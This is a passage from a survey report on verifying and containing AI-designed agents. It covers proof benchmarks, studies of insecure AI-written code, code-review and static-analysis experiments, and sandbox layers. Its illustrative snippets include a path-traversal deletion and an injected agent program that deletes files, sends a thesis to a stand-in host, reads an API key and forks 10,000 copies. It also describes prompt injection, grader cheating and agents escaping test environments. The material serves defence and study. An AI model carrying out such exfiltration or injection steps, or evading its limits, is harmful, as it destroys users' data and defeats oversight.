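| VeriContest | Proof | 13.8% (May 2026) | 100%, in Lean (October 2026) |
| CLEVER | All three | 0.6% (2025) | 36.6% (May 2026) |

The VERINA proof score counts a task as resolved if the system proves that the program meets its specification or proves that it does not. An earlier system by the company Harmonic resolved 183 tasks, 160 with proofs and the other 23 with refutations, so some of the benchmark's own statements were apparently false.

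The two VeriContest scores come from different conditions. GPT-5.5 had one attempt at a Verus proof. Serbanuta and colleagues, who develop the verifier they tested, used the newer Claude Opus 5.5. Their agents could submit a Lean proof up to 40 times, revising it after each error. The median proof took 3.4 minutes and cost $1.20. The team also ran Claude on the benchmark's own Verus task, using the 50 problems with the longest reference proofs and allowing up to ten attempts each. Claude proved 49 of them, 18 on the first attempt, so most of the rise in score does not depend on the switch to Lean.

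CLEVER's scoring understates what current agents can do, because it requires a specification equivalent to the benchmark's own, which is often faulty. Sosso and colleagues also counted programs that agents proved to meet their own specifications, if the agents judged those specifications to be valid readings of the task. By this measure, the best agent succeeded on 151 of the 157 feasible tasks.

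*A benchmark for vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025) is the largest of these collections, with 12,504 specifications. The researchers gave models a specification and asked for both code and a proof that the code meets it. The success rates were 82% in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean, though the sets of tasks differ between the languages. They also reported that models' success rate on an older Dafny benchmark rose from 68% to 96% within a year. The 96% combines the successes of several models, and the best single model reached about 89%, according to *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026).

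Most of these tasks involve a single function, whereas an agent may have many interacting modules. *Vero* (Ye, Lou et al., 2026) tested agents on 43 whole code repositories with specifications supplied. GPT-5.5 proved 87.3% of the individual specifications but completed only 27 repositories, because the remaining proofs needed facts that hold across many functions. Of the specifications it failed to prove, 14% failed because the grader rejected the attempt as cheating. In five cases, an agent replaced a reference algorithm with a simpler one that was easier to verify but less efficient. This was legitimate because the specifications did not mention speed.

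Ganguly and colleagues generated tasks about Rust programs translated into Lean, where a proof must also handle details such as arithmetic overflow. Their system proved 52.7% of a sample of 2,000 statements, with a limit of 30 minutes each. Some of the unproved statements may be false, because a model wrote them.

### What progress in mathematics does not supply

Machine-checked mathematics has advanced even faster. PutnamBench contains 672 formal versions of problems from a North American undergraduate mathematics competition. In August 2025 the system Seed-Prover solved just over half of them. In October 2026 Ganguly and colleagues reported solving 669, as well as all six problems of the 2026 International Mathematical Olympiad. They used the same system as for code, built on Anthropic's general model Fable 5 without further training.

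In these competitions, the prover receives a problem that someone has already translated into Lean, and a mathematician can usually compare the few lines of formal text with the original. For most software, nobody has written a formal specification. A better prover makes it easier to show that a program meets a given specification, including a wrong one, but does not identify the specification the user needed.

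Proof attempts help find some mistakes in specifications. Wang and colleagues wrote two versions of each specification, one for proofs and one that a computer can run on test cases, and then tried to prove that the two agree. This exposed errors in 31 of 3,037 problems that had passed all the tests and the AI judges. But two versions can share the same misunderstanding, and experts who read 300 of the problems found nine such cases.

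### Restricting what code can express

Another approach is to choose a few properties in advance and restrict the language so that a checker can prove them for every program it accepts. The Linux kernel does this with eBPF, a system that lets users load small programs into the kernel, for example to filter network traffic. Before a program runs, the eBPF verifier follows the possible paths through it and tracks the range of values each variable could hold. It rejects the program if any path might read memory outside the permitted areas or use a value that was never set, or if the check requires examining more than a million instructions. It rejected all loops until 2019, and now allows those it can prove will end. The verifier also rejects some safe programs, which programmers then have to rewrite.

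The eBPF verifier has had serious bugs. In CVE-2020-8835, it miscalculated the ranges of 32-bit numbers, so a program that passed could read and overwrite kernel memory. In CVE-2023-2163, it skipped paths that it wrongly treated as equivalent to ones it had already checked. Many Linux distributions now let only privileged users load eBPF programs. *Verifying the Verifier* (Vishwanathan et al., 2023) formally checked the range calculations in 16 kernel versions, found new bugs in older versions, and proved the calculations correct in the latest version examined. The verifier is hard to get right partly because it is large. It needs many thousands of lines of code to establish that a program is safe, whereas proof-carrying code leaves that work to the producer and needs only a small checker.

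For agents, the restricted language can be a typed workflow graph, in which each node is a model call or a tool and each connection carries a declared type of data. A checker can then reject a graph that passes free text to a step expecting a list of files. According to *RobustSGPO* (Zhao, Shi and colleagues, 2026), the design loop AgentFlow searches such graphs and checks them before execution. The paper's own system restricts the edits instead. It names the parts of the agent that the model should change and rejects any patch that does not change exactly those parts. Fixed code carries out edits that add or remove a whole component, and 28 of 36 such edits were valid, compared with 22 of 45 when the model made them freely. Zhao and colleagues note that checking which parts changed does not show that an edit is correct.

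*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) presents CaMeL, a system that restricts where data may flow. It addresses prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in text that an agent will read. One model sees only the user's request and writes a program for it in a small subset of Python. A second model, which has no tools, extracts values such as e-mail addresses from untrusted text. A custom interpreter runs the program, labels every value with its source and permitted readers, and checks the labels against a security policy before each tool call.

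Suppose a user asks the agent to send meeting notes to a colleague, and the notes contain a hidden instruction to forward all passwords. The instruction cannot add a step to the program, because the model that wrote the program never saw the notes. If the notes supply a false address for the colleague, the policy can block the message or require the user to confirm it. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of such attacks, CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks with these guarantees, compared with 84% for an undefended system. Someone still has to write the policies, and the labels do not stop a hidden instruction from making a summary misleading.

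### Which properties of an agent have a specification

Tool permissions, data flow and termination are the clearest candidates for proof today. A checker can show that a workflow calls only the tools on a list, if none of them runs arbitrary code, and that data with a certain label never reaches a certain tool. It can also show that an agent stops after a fixed number of model calls if its loops have fixed limits and every call returns or times out. The self-criticism loop in the `forward` function from Hu and colleagues is easy to check for this because it has a limit of five attempts. All these proofs hold whatever text the foundation model returns.

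There is no agreed formal specification of a helpful answer, a fair summary or good judgement about when to ask the user. A developer can substitute something measurable, such as a minimum score from a judge model, but a proof would then establish only that the agent reaches this score, which leaves room for objective hacking. Many other practical rules can be formally specified once their terms are defined. For example, compliance with "delete only temporary files" becomes provable once someone defines a temporary file, but if the definition is poor, an agent that complies with it can still delete a user's thesis.

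### Advocates and critics

Bursuc and colleagues argue that testing can reveal bugs but cannot prove that none remain. They cite the 2024 CrowdStrike outage, in which a faulty update disrupted 8.5 million devices. They think verification could become a built-in last step of compilers, and that people might one day write only specifications. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) extends the idea to AI in general. It proposes combining a mathematical model of the world, a specification of acceptable effects and a verifier that certifies the AI system against both. Ganguly and colleagues argue that a system trained on test results may learn to exploit the tests, a risk that applies directly to design loops. They add that a proof covers all inputs and takes little compute to check.

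Critics have long questioned what such proofs establish. De Millo, Lipton and Perlis argued in 1979 that mathematicians come to trust a theorem because colleagues read, discuss and use its proof, and that nobody would do this for the long and tedious proofs of programs. The philosopher James Fetzer objected in 1988 that a proof concerns an abstract program, while a running program's behaviour also depends on a physical machine. Vempaty and colleagues, who do not oppose verification, show that the verification rate can be high even when specifications are almost empty.

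Small proof checkers have weakened the 1979 objection because people no longer need to read the proofs, though they still need to read the specifications. Fetzer's objection is strongest for agents that act on websites, people and money, because proofs about such agents need assumptions about how those things behave. It matters less for a rule that a small interpreter can enforce, such as a ban on a particular tool.

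It is still unclear how far the recent successes carry over to ordinary software. Serbanuta and colleagues also verify code for customers, but they have to write the specifications for that code from scratch, and they do not yet know how much of their benchmark result will hold for it.

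## Experiments on finding faults by reading code

If a program has no written specification, checking it before its first run depends on reading the code. The reader can be a person, a static analyser or another AI system. Researchers test these readers on code with known faults and measure the detection rate, which is the share of the faults found, and false alarms, which are warnings about code without faults. These experiments use ordinary software, so they are only indirect evidence about agents written by design loops.

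### How often working code is insecure

A design loop keeps the agents that score well, so an auditor mostly has to find faults that do not lower the score. Many security faults do not lower it, because a program can do everything its user asked for and still let an attacker in.

Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Is Vibe Coding Safe?*, built a benchmark called SusVibes to measure how often this happens. They chose 186 features of Python projects whose original code had a vulnerability that was later fixed. They removed the code for each feature, asked an AI agent to write it again, and ran hidden tests for both function and security. The best agent, built on Claude 4 Sonnet, wrote working code for 57.0% of the tasks, but only 11.8% of the tasks had code that was both working and secure. In one failure, the agent's password check for the web framework Django returned early for accounts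 without a usable password. The check gave correct results, but an attacker could tell from the response time which usernames existed.

Newer models do better. *Fable 5.1 takes the top spot* (Compagna, 2026) reports results from the security company Endor Labs on SusVibes tasks. Claude Fable 5.1 wrote working code for 87.2% of the tasks and working, secure code for 37.4%. These figures exclude tasks with overly strict tests and give no credit for fixes that the model had memorised.

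*Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) tested six agents on 450 tasks based on 150 real vulnerabilities in seven programming languages. The agents wrote working code for 73.6% to 91.3% of the tasks. The best agent, Claude Fable 5, wrote code that both worked and was secure for 25.1% of them.

| Test | Model | Working | Working and secure | Insecure share of working code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
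| SusVibes (Zhao and colleagues) | Claude 4 Sonnet | 57.0% | 11.8% | 79% |
| SusVibes tasks (Compagna) | Claude Fable 5.1 | 87.2% | 37.4% | 57% |
| Last Secure Code Benchmark (Wu and colleagues) | GPT-5.6 Sol | 89.1% | 24.7% | 72% |
| The same, with a security reminder | GPT-5.6 Sol | 87.6% | 46.2% | 47% |

Every task behind these percentages comes from a place where a programmer had already made a security mistake, so the percentages are not estimates for ordinary code. *BaxBench* (2025) starts instead from 28 kinds of web application, which yield 392 tasks, and attacks each finished program with real exploits. In a small rerun, *Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (2026) found that an exploit succeeded against about a third (22 of 68) of the applications written without special security instructions.

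In the tests by Wu and colleagues, the agents wrote working, secure code in 34.3% of attempts at memory-safety tasks, but in only 0.7% of attempts at tasks where the risk was exposing information. The defence in memory-safety tasks is usually a local check, such as whether an index is within bounds. Preventing exposure depends on a policy that the task description never states, such as which data a reply may reveal.

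An agent's own tests may miss such faults. Kimi K3 rebuilt a Java class that imports uploaded archives and wrote 33 checks for it. The class passed all 14 hidden functional tests, but it would create any type of object named in an uploaded file, and it failed all four security tests. Two other agents avoided the fault by using a safe version of the same parser.

When Wu and colleagues retested four models with a one-sentence request for secure code, three of them produced working, secure code 15 to 21 percentage points more often. The fourth, DeepSeek V4 Pro, improved by only 1.1 points. Even with the request, most tasks ended in code that was insecure or did not work.

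*Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (2026) compared agents that wrote web back ends from scratch with agents that worked next to existing code. Agents produced secure results less often when the existing code was insecure and more often when it was secure. A loop that shows the meta agent its archive might spread faults in the same way, though the experiment did not test this.

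### Human reviewers

In ordinary software development, a programmer submits a change as a pull request, and other developers read it before it becomes part of the main code. They see the changed lines, usually with a short description, and comment on anything that looks wrong.

In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) tested how well developers find security faults in code review. They wrote a 160-line Java change for registering users of a web service and planted two faults in it. When a database error occurred, the program wrote the user's e-mail address and unencrypted password to a log file. It also protected passwords with MD5, a hash function that attackers can break quickly. Two security engineers found both faults in a trial.

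The 150 participants fell into four groups. One group received no security instructions. Another learned that the researchers were interested in security and read a definition of a vulnerability. The remaining two groups received the same information plus a checklist, either a general one with 22 items or one with seven items chosen for this change.

| Instructions | Found the password in the log | Found the weak hash function |
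|---|---|---|
| None about security | 1 of 33 (3%) | 7 of 33 (21%) |
| Look for security faults | 19 of 41 (46%) | 25 of 41 (61%) |
| The same, with general checklist | 16 of 35 (46%) | 20 of 35 (57%) |
| The same, with tailored checklist | 19 of 41 (46%) | 28 of 41 (68%) |

Telling reviewers to look for security faults greatly improved detection, but neither checklist improved it significantly further. More than half of the instructed reviewers still missed the password in the log, even though the tailored checklist had an item pointing to it. Participants who missed a fault often said they had focused on other things or lacked the necessary knowledge. Three people without security instructions said that finding the weak hash function was not their responsibility.

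This matters for how a design loop asks for a review. The self-review instructions in Meta Agent Search cover novelty, correctness and performance, so they are closer to the instructions the first group received. A reviewer who is supposed to find unwanted deletions or network access should probably be told explicitly to look for them.

The experiment was limited to one change and two faults, and most people who opened the study did not finish it. It measured only whether participants found the two faults, so it gives no false-alarm rate. Braz and colleagues cite another experiment in which students using a checklist raised half as many false alarms during formal code inspections. Other experiments found no clear benefit from checklists.

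Yang, He and colleagues (2026), in *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?*, collected confirmed bugs from open-source projects and traced each to the pull request that introduced it. Human reviewers had caught about half of these bugs before the code was merged, and the rest were found later. The true detection rate is probably lower, because the records omit bugs that nobody has noticed.

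### Static analysers

The simplest static analysers search a program for known patterns. For example, a rule that flags every use of MD5 would have found the weak hash function in the experiment above. Semgrep, a popular analyser, mostly uses rules like this.

Other faults only become visible when an analyser follows data through the program. CodeQL, a tool from GitHub, converts source code into a database that includes data-flow graphs, as *Security of LLM-generated Code* (2026) describes. Users then run queries on the database to look for particular weaknesses. Consider this part of an agent:

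```
reply = model("Which file is out of date? " + task)
path  = "/data/" + reply
delete(path)
```

If the model returns `../home/ana/thesis.txt`, the path leads out of the data folder and the agent deletes the thesis. A pattern rule could flag the call to `delete`, but it would also flag every harmless clean-up routine. A data-flow query treats the model's reply as a source of untrusted text and `delete` as a sink, where that text can do damage. It traces the text from `reply` to `path` to `delete` and reports the route unless the program checks the path along the way. This works only if someone has listed `model` as a source and defined what counts as a sufficient check.

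Analysers miss many faults in AI-written code. *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?* (2026) cites a comparison on programs that GitHub Copilot, an AI coding assistant, wrote for tasks that each targeted a particular weakness. The analyser CodeQL reported the targeted weakness in 18.46% of the programs, while people who inspected them found it in 73.84%. If the manual findings are right, CodeQL detected at most a quarter of the cases.

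That comparison relies on human judgement, but exploits are a more direct test. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) ran Semgrep on BaxBench applications that DeepSeek V4.1 Flash wrote. Semgrep flagged only 32.4% of the applications that an exploit could break. On another benchmark, RiskyPy, analysers flagged 80.0% to 93.8% of the insecure programs, but its creators had chosen tasks whose solutions analysers tend to flag. The flags were also barely better than chance at identifying insecure code, because the analysers often flagged secure programs too.

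If a design loop produced code like these BaxBench applications and rejected everything Semgrep flagged, it would still run about two thirds of the exploitable programs and would also discard sound ones.

The choice of analyser also affects the result. *LLM-CSEC* (2025) applied several tools to the same C and C++ code from ten models. CodeQL reported 37 types of weakness and Snyk Code reported 10. When the models were instructed to write secure code, the count fell to 29 with CodeQL but rose to 12 with Snyk Code, so whether the instruction appeared to help depended on the tool.

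Text searches can also count a comment as a defence. Wu and colleagues found that many of the vulnerability tests in an existing collection inspected the source text, and that a program could sometimes pass by including a particular comment. They rewrote the tests to attack the running program. Static analysis is more dependable for narrow questions about the text, such as whether an agent imports a networking library. It gives the same answer every time and costs very little per program.

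### AI reviewers

An AI reviewer receives the changed code, often with access to the rest of the project, and writes comments as a human reviewer would. Some reviewers are a single model call, while others are agents that can search files and run tests before commenting.

*Code Review Agent Benchmark* (Zhang, Ruan and colleagues, 2026) compares AI code review tools with human reviewers. Its benchmark, c-CRAB, contains 184 pull requests and 234 tests based on human reviewers' comments. An AI tool reviews the original code without seeing those comments. A coding agent then revises the code according to the AI review, and the tests check whether the revision resolves the human reviewer's concern. The four tools each succeeded on between 20.1% and 32.1% of the tests, and at least one tool succeeded on 41.5% of the tests when their results were combined.

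These results understate how many problems the tools found. In one case, a human reviewer asked for a text field without a length limit because long names might not fit. Claude Code found the same problem but suggested raising the limit, so the revised code failed the test. Like this test, 192 of the 234 tests check the source text for a particular change. Zhang and colleagues also read 92 of the AI comments and judged 84% of them useful, though many concerned issues that the human reviewers had not raised.

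Two other benchmarks use confirmed bugs instead of human comments. *CR-Bench-v2* (Pereira, Sinha and colleagues, 2026) tested reviewers on 174 pull requests, each with one known bug. The best systems found about a third of the bugs. Gemini Code Assist, a commercial product, found only 8.1%, although AI judges rated 78.0% of its comments as useful. A team that judged Gemini Code Assist only by the quality of its comments would have overestimated how many bugs it catches.

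The strongest results come from CRBugBench, which Yang and colleagues built from the bugs they had traced. It contains 1,000 pull requests from 98 open-source projects. Claude Opus 5 identified the known bug among its first five comments in 71.9% of cases, compared with 47.7% for Claude Opus 4.6, a model about five months older.

| Benchmark | What the reviewer had to find | Best single system | Detection rate |
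|---|---|---|---|
| c-CRAB (March 2026) | 234 concerns of human reviewers | Claude Code | 32.1% |
| CR-Bench-v2 (November 2026) | 174 known bugs | GPT-5-mini with self-reflection | 33.7% |
| CRBugBench (October 2026) | 1,000 known bugs | Claude Opus 5 | 71.9% |

Newer models probably explain much of the gap between the last two rows. GPT-5-mini found 33.7% of the bugs in one benchmark and about 44% in the other. The 71.9% is therefore the better guide to current reviewers, at least for open-source code.

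On two large private codebases, the reviewers' performance fell by up to 25.5%. Yang and colleagues attribute part of this drop to bugs that are not visible in the changed lines and can only be found with knowledge of the wider project. The reviewers also did worse on long changes and on changes that mixed several kinds of file. They spent most of their time reading and searching, and Opus 5 ran code in only 9.7% of its turns.

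Some reviewers trusted misleading descriptions or comments. A design loop can produce these without any intent to deceive, as with the comment in the ARC agent that had the jumbled advice.

Human and AI reviewers catch partly different bugs. In the CRBugBench data, human reviewers caught about 50% of the bugs before the merge, the best AI reviewer caught 71.9%, and together they would have caught 82.1%. People were better at noticing code that would be hard to maintain, while the AI reviewers were better at catching severe bugs and reliability problems. But the combined figure holds only if people review just as carefully when they can see AI comments. Yang and colleagues cite a controlled experiment in which AI reviews increased the number of minor issues that expert developers found, but not the number of severe ones, and saved no time.

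### False alarms from AI reviewers

CRBugBench measures only whether a reviewer finds the known bug. To measure false alarms, researchers also need code that they know to be clean. *Can LLMs Catch a Rigged Backtest?* (2026) provides pairs of flawed and clean backtests, which are programs that test an investment strategy on past data. With an open-ended prompt, AI reviewers detected 35 of 48 flawed programs but also raised needless concerns at a rate of 45 per 48 clean ones, so their objections give a design loop little basis for choosing between programs.

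This result depended heavily on the wording of the prompt. A more restrictive prompt raised detection to 100% and cut the false-alarm rate on code from 93.8% to 20.8%. A "clean-aware" prompt removed the remaining false alarms for the DeepSeek model tested, without losing any detections. These programs contained a limited set of faults, so the result may not hold for agent code, where nobody knows in advance which faults to expect.

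Using another model to filter out bad comments may not help much, because most false alarms would get through. *CRJudgeBench* (2026) asked models to judge 359 review comments, of which 130 were plausible but wrong. The models recognised 88% to 99% of the valid comments but, without special training, only 2% to 21% of the invalid ones.

Agent code is also difficult to review because it includes prompts as well as program statements. *AI Cannot Review What Humans Catch* (2026) tested AI reviewers on instruction files for coding agents, which resemble prompts. OpenCode raised only 3.9% of the concerns that human reviewers raised, and Claude raised 3.2%. As with c-CRAB, a low rate does not show that the AI reviewers' other comments were useless, but some were plainly wrong. For example, OpenCode praised one file for its correct folder structure, although the file referred to a folder that did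 not exist.

### Whether a model misses its own mistakes

In many loops the same model writes the code and reviews it, so its blind spots could affect both steps. *Cross-Context Review* (2026) compared a model that reviewed its work in the same session with one that received only the finished work in a new session. The new session gave better results, even when the model in the original session reviewed its work twice. The earlier conversation probably anchors the model's judgement, and a loop can easily remove this influence by starting a new session for each review.

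Reviewing code in a fresh session does not help a model find faults that it consistently overlooks. The results from Wu and colleagues suggest that different models overlook different faults. The best single model wrote working, secure code for 113 of the 450 tasks, but at least one of the six models did so for 198, and none did for the other 252. A reviewer from another developer might therefore notice some faults that the first model tends to write. This evidence is indirect, since a model that avoids a fault in its own code may still miss it in someone else's.

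Different models also make many of the same errors. *When Does a Second Model Help?* (2026) cites a study of more than 350 language models. On one leaderboard, two models that both got a question wrong chose the same wrong answer about 60% of the time. Larger and more accurate models had more strongly correlated errors. Approvals from two different models therefore give less assurance than two independent checks would.

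A second model also has to add more than a repeat review by the first model would. The same paper found that reviews by one model overlapped by only 52.2%, so a repeat review can add findings too. A reviewer that can edit the code can also introduce new faults. *Cross-Model LLM Code Review* (2026) therefore tests the final program and counts the reviewer's fixes and regressions separately.

### The reviewing load of one run

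Hu and colleagues' argument that readable code is easier to audit also depends on how much code there is to read. Suppose a loop makes 80 changes, as many as the main run of the Darwin Gödel Machine produced agents, and each change has 189 lines, the median in CRBugBench. A reviewer would have to read 15,120 lines. Human reading speed varies with the code and the purpose of the review, so assume a rate of 200 lines an hour:

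80 × 189 ÷ 200 ≈ 76 hours

At 400 lines an hour, the work would take 38 hours. The Darwin Gödel Machine run lasted about two weeks, so one full-time reviewer could roughly have kept pace with it even at the slower rate. A Meta-Harness search evaluates about 60 programs in a few hours. If each required 189 lines of reading, a reviewer would need 57 hours at that rate, so waiting for approval before each program's first run would greatly slow the loop.

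These figures cover one reading of the changed lines, but not of the surrounding code, the logs, or the repaired versions of crashing programs. A strict rule would also require someone to read each repaired version before it runs.

AI review is much faster. According to Yang and colleagues, Claude Opus 5 took 9.8 minutes and cost $2.97 per pull request on average. At that rate, reviewing 80 changes one after another would take about 13 hours and cost about $238. Reviewing them in parallel would take less time. If its reviews were of average length, Opus 5 would write about 500 comments totaling 94,000 words, and someone would still have to decide which comments to act on.

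Even then, some faults would probably remain. If 8 of the 80 changes each contained a fault, and the reviewer had an independent 71.9% chance of finding each one, it would miss about two on average. The chance of finding all eight would be 7%.

### Adding an audit to the cost of design

Audits also affect whether automated design is worth its cost. El and colleagues divide the cost of a designed agent into a fixed cost C<sub>0</sub> for writing and evaluating all the candidates, and a cost C<sub>i</sub> for each example the finished agent handles. After n examples, the total is C<sub>0</sub> + n · C<sub>i</sub>. An existing hand-designed agent has no new design cost, so the automatically designed one must make up for C<sub>0</sub> by producing correct answers at a lower cost.

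In the experiments, the designed agents became cheaper per correct answer after about 15,000 examples on DROP, which tests reading comprehension, and MMLU, which contains questions on many academic subjects. On both datasets, the meta agent saw only the seven starting agents. On the two other datasets, the designed agents never became cheaper per correct answer, however many examples they handled.

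An audit before release adds a fixed cost A, so the total becomes C<sub>0</sub> + A + n · C<sub>i</sub>. To see how this changes the break-even point, let p be the designed agent's share of correct answers, and let q and c be the hand-designed agent's share of correct answers and cost per example. The two agents cost the same per correct answer when

(C<sub>0</sub> + A + n · C<sub>i</sub>) / (n · p) = c / q

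Solving for n gives

n = (C<sub>0</sub> + A) / (p · c / q − C<sub>i</sub>)

The audit does not change the saving per example, which is the denominator, so the break-even point grows in proportion to the fixed cost. For the two datasets, it rises from 15,000 examples to 15,000 × (1 + A / C<sub>0</sub>), where A is the cost of the audit and C<sub>0</sub> is the cost of the design run. If the two costs are equal, the break-even point doubles to 30,000. If the saving per example is zero or negative, the designed agent never breaks even, with or without an audit.

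The following example uses 30 iterations, as El and colleagues did, and assumes the other values. The design run costs $300, each agent has 50 lines, and a human reviewer reads 200 lines an hour for $100. The AI reviewer costs $2.97 per agent, a figure based on pull requests, which probably cost more to review than short programs.

| Audit | Audit cost A | Break-even point |
|---|---|---|
| None | $0 | 15,000 examples |
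| A person reads only the released agent | $25 | 16,250 |
| An AI reviewer reads all 30 agents | $89 | about 19,500 |
| A person reads all 30 agents | $750 | 52,500 |

Reading only the released agent takes little effort, but it does not address harm done during earlier runs. The calculation also assumes that the audit approves the best agent. If the loop has to release a weaker one, p falls and the break-even point rises further. If people still check the agent's answers after release, that work adds to C<sub>i</sub> and may eliminate the saving.

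As models get cheaper, human review makes up a larger share of the total cost. If all model prices in this example fell to a tenth, the design run would cost $30, but a person would still charge $750 to read the 30 agents. The saving per example would also fall to a tenth. The break-even point would stay at 15,000 examples without an audit, but would rise from 52,500 to 390,000 with the full human audit.

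## Sandboxes and execution limits

Sandboxes and execution limits reduce the harm a program can do even when reviewers have missed its faults, but they depend on software that may be faulty or badly configured. In 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic disclosed that AI agents had reached real systems from test environments that should have had no internet access.

### Layers of isolation

A program has to make a system call to open a file, send data or start another program. A system call is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Most forms of isolation restrict these requests or change which kernel handles them.

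Process permissions are the simplest layer. The loop runs each generated agent under a separate user account, and the kernel blocks access to other accounts' files. A system-call filter, such as seccomp on Linux, also blocks whole types of request, like loading new code into the kernel. Both add almost no overhead. They fail if the kernel has an exploitable flaw in a call that the filter permits, or if the filter's author forgot to block a dangerous call.

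A container gives a program its own view of the machine, with separate files, processes and network connections. Containers suit design loops because they start quickly and each agent can have a fresh copy of the same environment. But all containers on a machine share the host machine's kernel, so a kernel flaw can let a program escape its container and access the host.

gVisor, a system from Google, puts a second kernel between the program and the host. This kernel runs as an ordinary program, which is why engineers call it a user-space kernel. It handles most system calls itself and makes only a limited set of requests to the host. To escape, a program usually needs one flaw in gVisor and another in the small part of the host kernel that gVisor uses. In return, file and network operations become slower, and some software does not run because gVisor lacks a system call it needs.

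Firecracker, from Amazon, runs small virtual machines. Each has its own Linux kernel, and the processor's virtualisation features separate its memory from the host's. A program that takes over this inner kernel is still inside the virtual machine, and can leave only through a flaw in Firecracker, in the part of the host kernel that manages virtual machines, or in the processor. Firecracker provides very few virtual devices, so there is less code to attack. A machine starts in a fraction of a second, so a loop can give every agent a new one.

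### Files, network connections and credentials

None of these layers restricts what a program does with the files and connections someone has deliberately given it. If a loop mounts the user's home folder with write permission inside a virtual machine, an agent can delete the user's files without escaping the virtual machine. A read-only mount lets the agent read the task files but not change them, and a temporary folder gives it somewhere to write.

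Network rules work best as a short list of permitted destinations, with everything else blocked. Each permitted destination needs scrutiny because it may connect to other systems. GitLab (2026) recommends treating any internal service that an untrusted program can reach as if it were exposed to the internet, since whatever takes over the program can also reach the service.

Agents built on a foundation model need at least a connection to the model. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), Anthropic asks outside organisations that test its unreleased models for cyberattack skills to block all other connections by default, keep the model's keys outside the test environment, and verify the configuration before every evaluation. A common way to withhold a key is to use a gateway, a small program outside the sandbox that receives the agent's prompt, adds the key and forwards the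 request, so the agent can use the model but cannot copy the key. The gateway should also switch off the model provider's web search, if there is one, or the agent could reach the internet through the model.

### One generated agent in the sandbox

Suppose a loop scores the following agent on questions about a folder of documents:

```
def forward(task):
    docs = read_all("/data")
    code = model("Write a program for this task: " + task + docs)
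    return run(code)
```

One document contains a hidden instruction, and the model replies with this program:

```
delete("/data/report.txt")
thesis = read("/home/ana/thesis.txt")
send("https://files.example", thesis)
key = read_setting("MODEL_KEY")
start 10,000 copies of this program
return "42"
```

To show every layer at work, assume that the program continues after each failed step.

| Action | What stops it | Result |
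|---|---|---|
| Delete the report | Read-only mount | The deletion fails |
| Read the thesis | No mount of the home folder; process permissions as a second barrier | The file does not exist inside the sandbox |
| Send the thesis away | Network rules | The connection fails |
| Read the model key | Withheld credentials | The setting is empty |
| Start 10,000 copies | Process limit | The kernel refuses new processes above the limit |
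| Return a wrong answer | Nothing | The evaluator receives "42" |

The system-call filter would block the program from loading code into the kernel. If the program exploited a flaw in a permitted call, it could take over the host from an ordinary container. In gVisor or Firecracker, that call would go to a kernel separate from the host's, so the program would need another flaw to reach the host.

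The correct answers should never enter the sandbox, so the evaluator has to score the agent's output outside it. The loop should also delete the sandbox after each agent runs, because leftover files could change the next agent's behaviour and score.

Text such as answers, error messages and logs has to leave the sandbox, and the loop may put it in the meta agent's next prompt. That text can contain hidden instructions, so the meta agent needs a sandbox too, especially in loops that edit their own code.

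### Limits and who enforces them

Different parts of the system enforce different limits. A supervising program outside the sandbox ends the run when its time limit expires. The Linux kernel can limit memory, processor time and the number of processes for a whole group of programs. The gateway is the natural place to limit model calls and spending because every call passes through it. A spending cap on the model provider account provides a backup if the gateway fails.

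Limits inside the agent's own code are unreliable. The `forward` function from Hu and colleagues stops after five attempts, but the meta agent wrote that number and could raise it in the next version. Design loops have altered their own limits in this way. A limit can also fail by accident, because many time limits in Python work by raising an error inside the program, and an agent with a general error handler may catch the error and carry on. Enforcing the limit with SIGKILL, which makes the kernel end the program immediately, avoids this problem because no program can catch that signal.

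Limits also have to cover everything an agent starts. If each process had its own allowance of 20 model calls, an agent could start ten processes and make 200 calls. A gateway can prevent this by counting all calls from a sandbox together. Such limits cap the resources a run can use, but a run that finishes within them does not show what the agent would do with more time.

Some loops treat a budget as part of the search. Liu, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Mendel Gödel Machine*, build on the Huxley-Gödel Machine, which divides a fixed budget between testing existing agents and creating new ones. If the loop has run N tests and has V agents, it creates another only when

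N<sup>α</sup> ≥ V

where α is a setting between 0 and 1. With α = 0.6, for example, 800 tests would permit about 55 agents. This rule spreads effort sensibly but does not limit spending, because one test may involve a single model call or thousands. In their simulations, Liu and colleagues give every edit the same cost as a test, but agents that nobody has run before may cost very different amounts.

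### A budget for one run

This example uses a search with 30 iterations and up to six versions of the agent in each, as in Meta Agent Search. The other values are assumed. Each version attempts 60 tasks, and a typical agent makes 10 model calls per task at $0.01 each. The gateway allows at most 40 calls per task and limits the length of prompts and replies so that no call costs more than $0.05.

| Part of the run | Typical cost | Highest cost under the limits |
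|---|---|---|
| One task | $0.10 | 40 × $0.05 = $2 |
| One version, 60 tasks | $6 | $120 |
| Whole search | 30 × $6 = $180 | 180 × $120 = $21,600 |
| Whole search with a total cap of $400 | $180 | $400 |

The limit per task allows four times the usual number of calls, so without a cap on the whole search, the bill could reach 120 times the typical cost. A total cap prevents this, but a few faulty agents could still use up the money meant for the others. A further limit of $12 per version leaves room for 18 such failures on top of 30 typical agents, since 18 × $12 is $216 and the search has $220 to spare.

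The gateway should reserve money for each call before forwarding it. Suppose the loop runs 20 tasks at once and each task sends all 40 of its calls together. If the gateway subtracts the cost only after a reply arrives, 800 calls worth up to $40 could start when the budget is almost empty. To prevent this, the gateway can reserve $0.05 per call and return what the call did not use.

The supervising program also needs a total time limit. With a limit of 10 minutes per task and 20 tasks running at once, one version can take 30 minutes and the whole search 90 hours. The loop must also record why each version stopped. Otherwise it may treat an exhausted budget as a crash, try to repair the agent and spend the money again, up to five times.

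OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) estimates that the company's system for detecting dangerous behaviour uses about 20% as much computing power as the model activity it covers. At that rate, monitoring this search would add about $36 to the typical cost of $180.

### OpenAI's July incident

The most detailed evidence on containment comes from testing and training models, not from design loops. But the conditions are similar, because the developers were running programs that a model had just written and no person had read.

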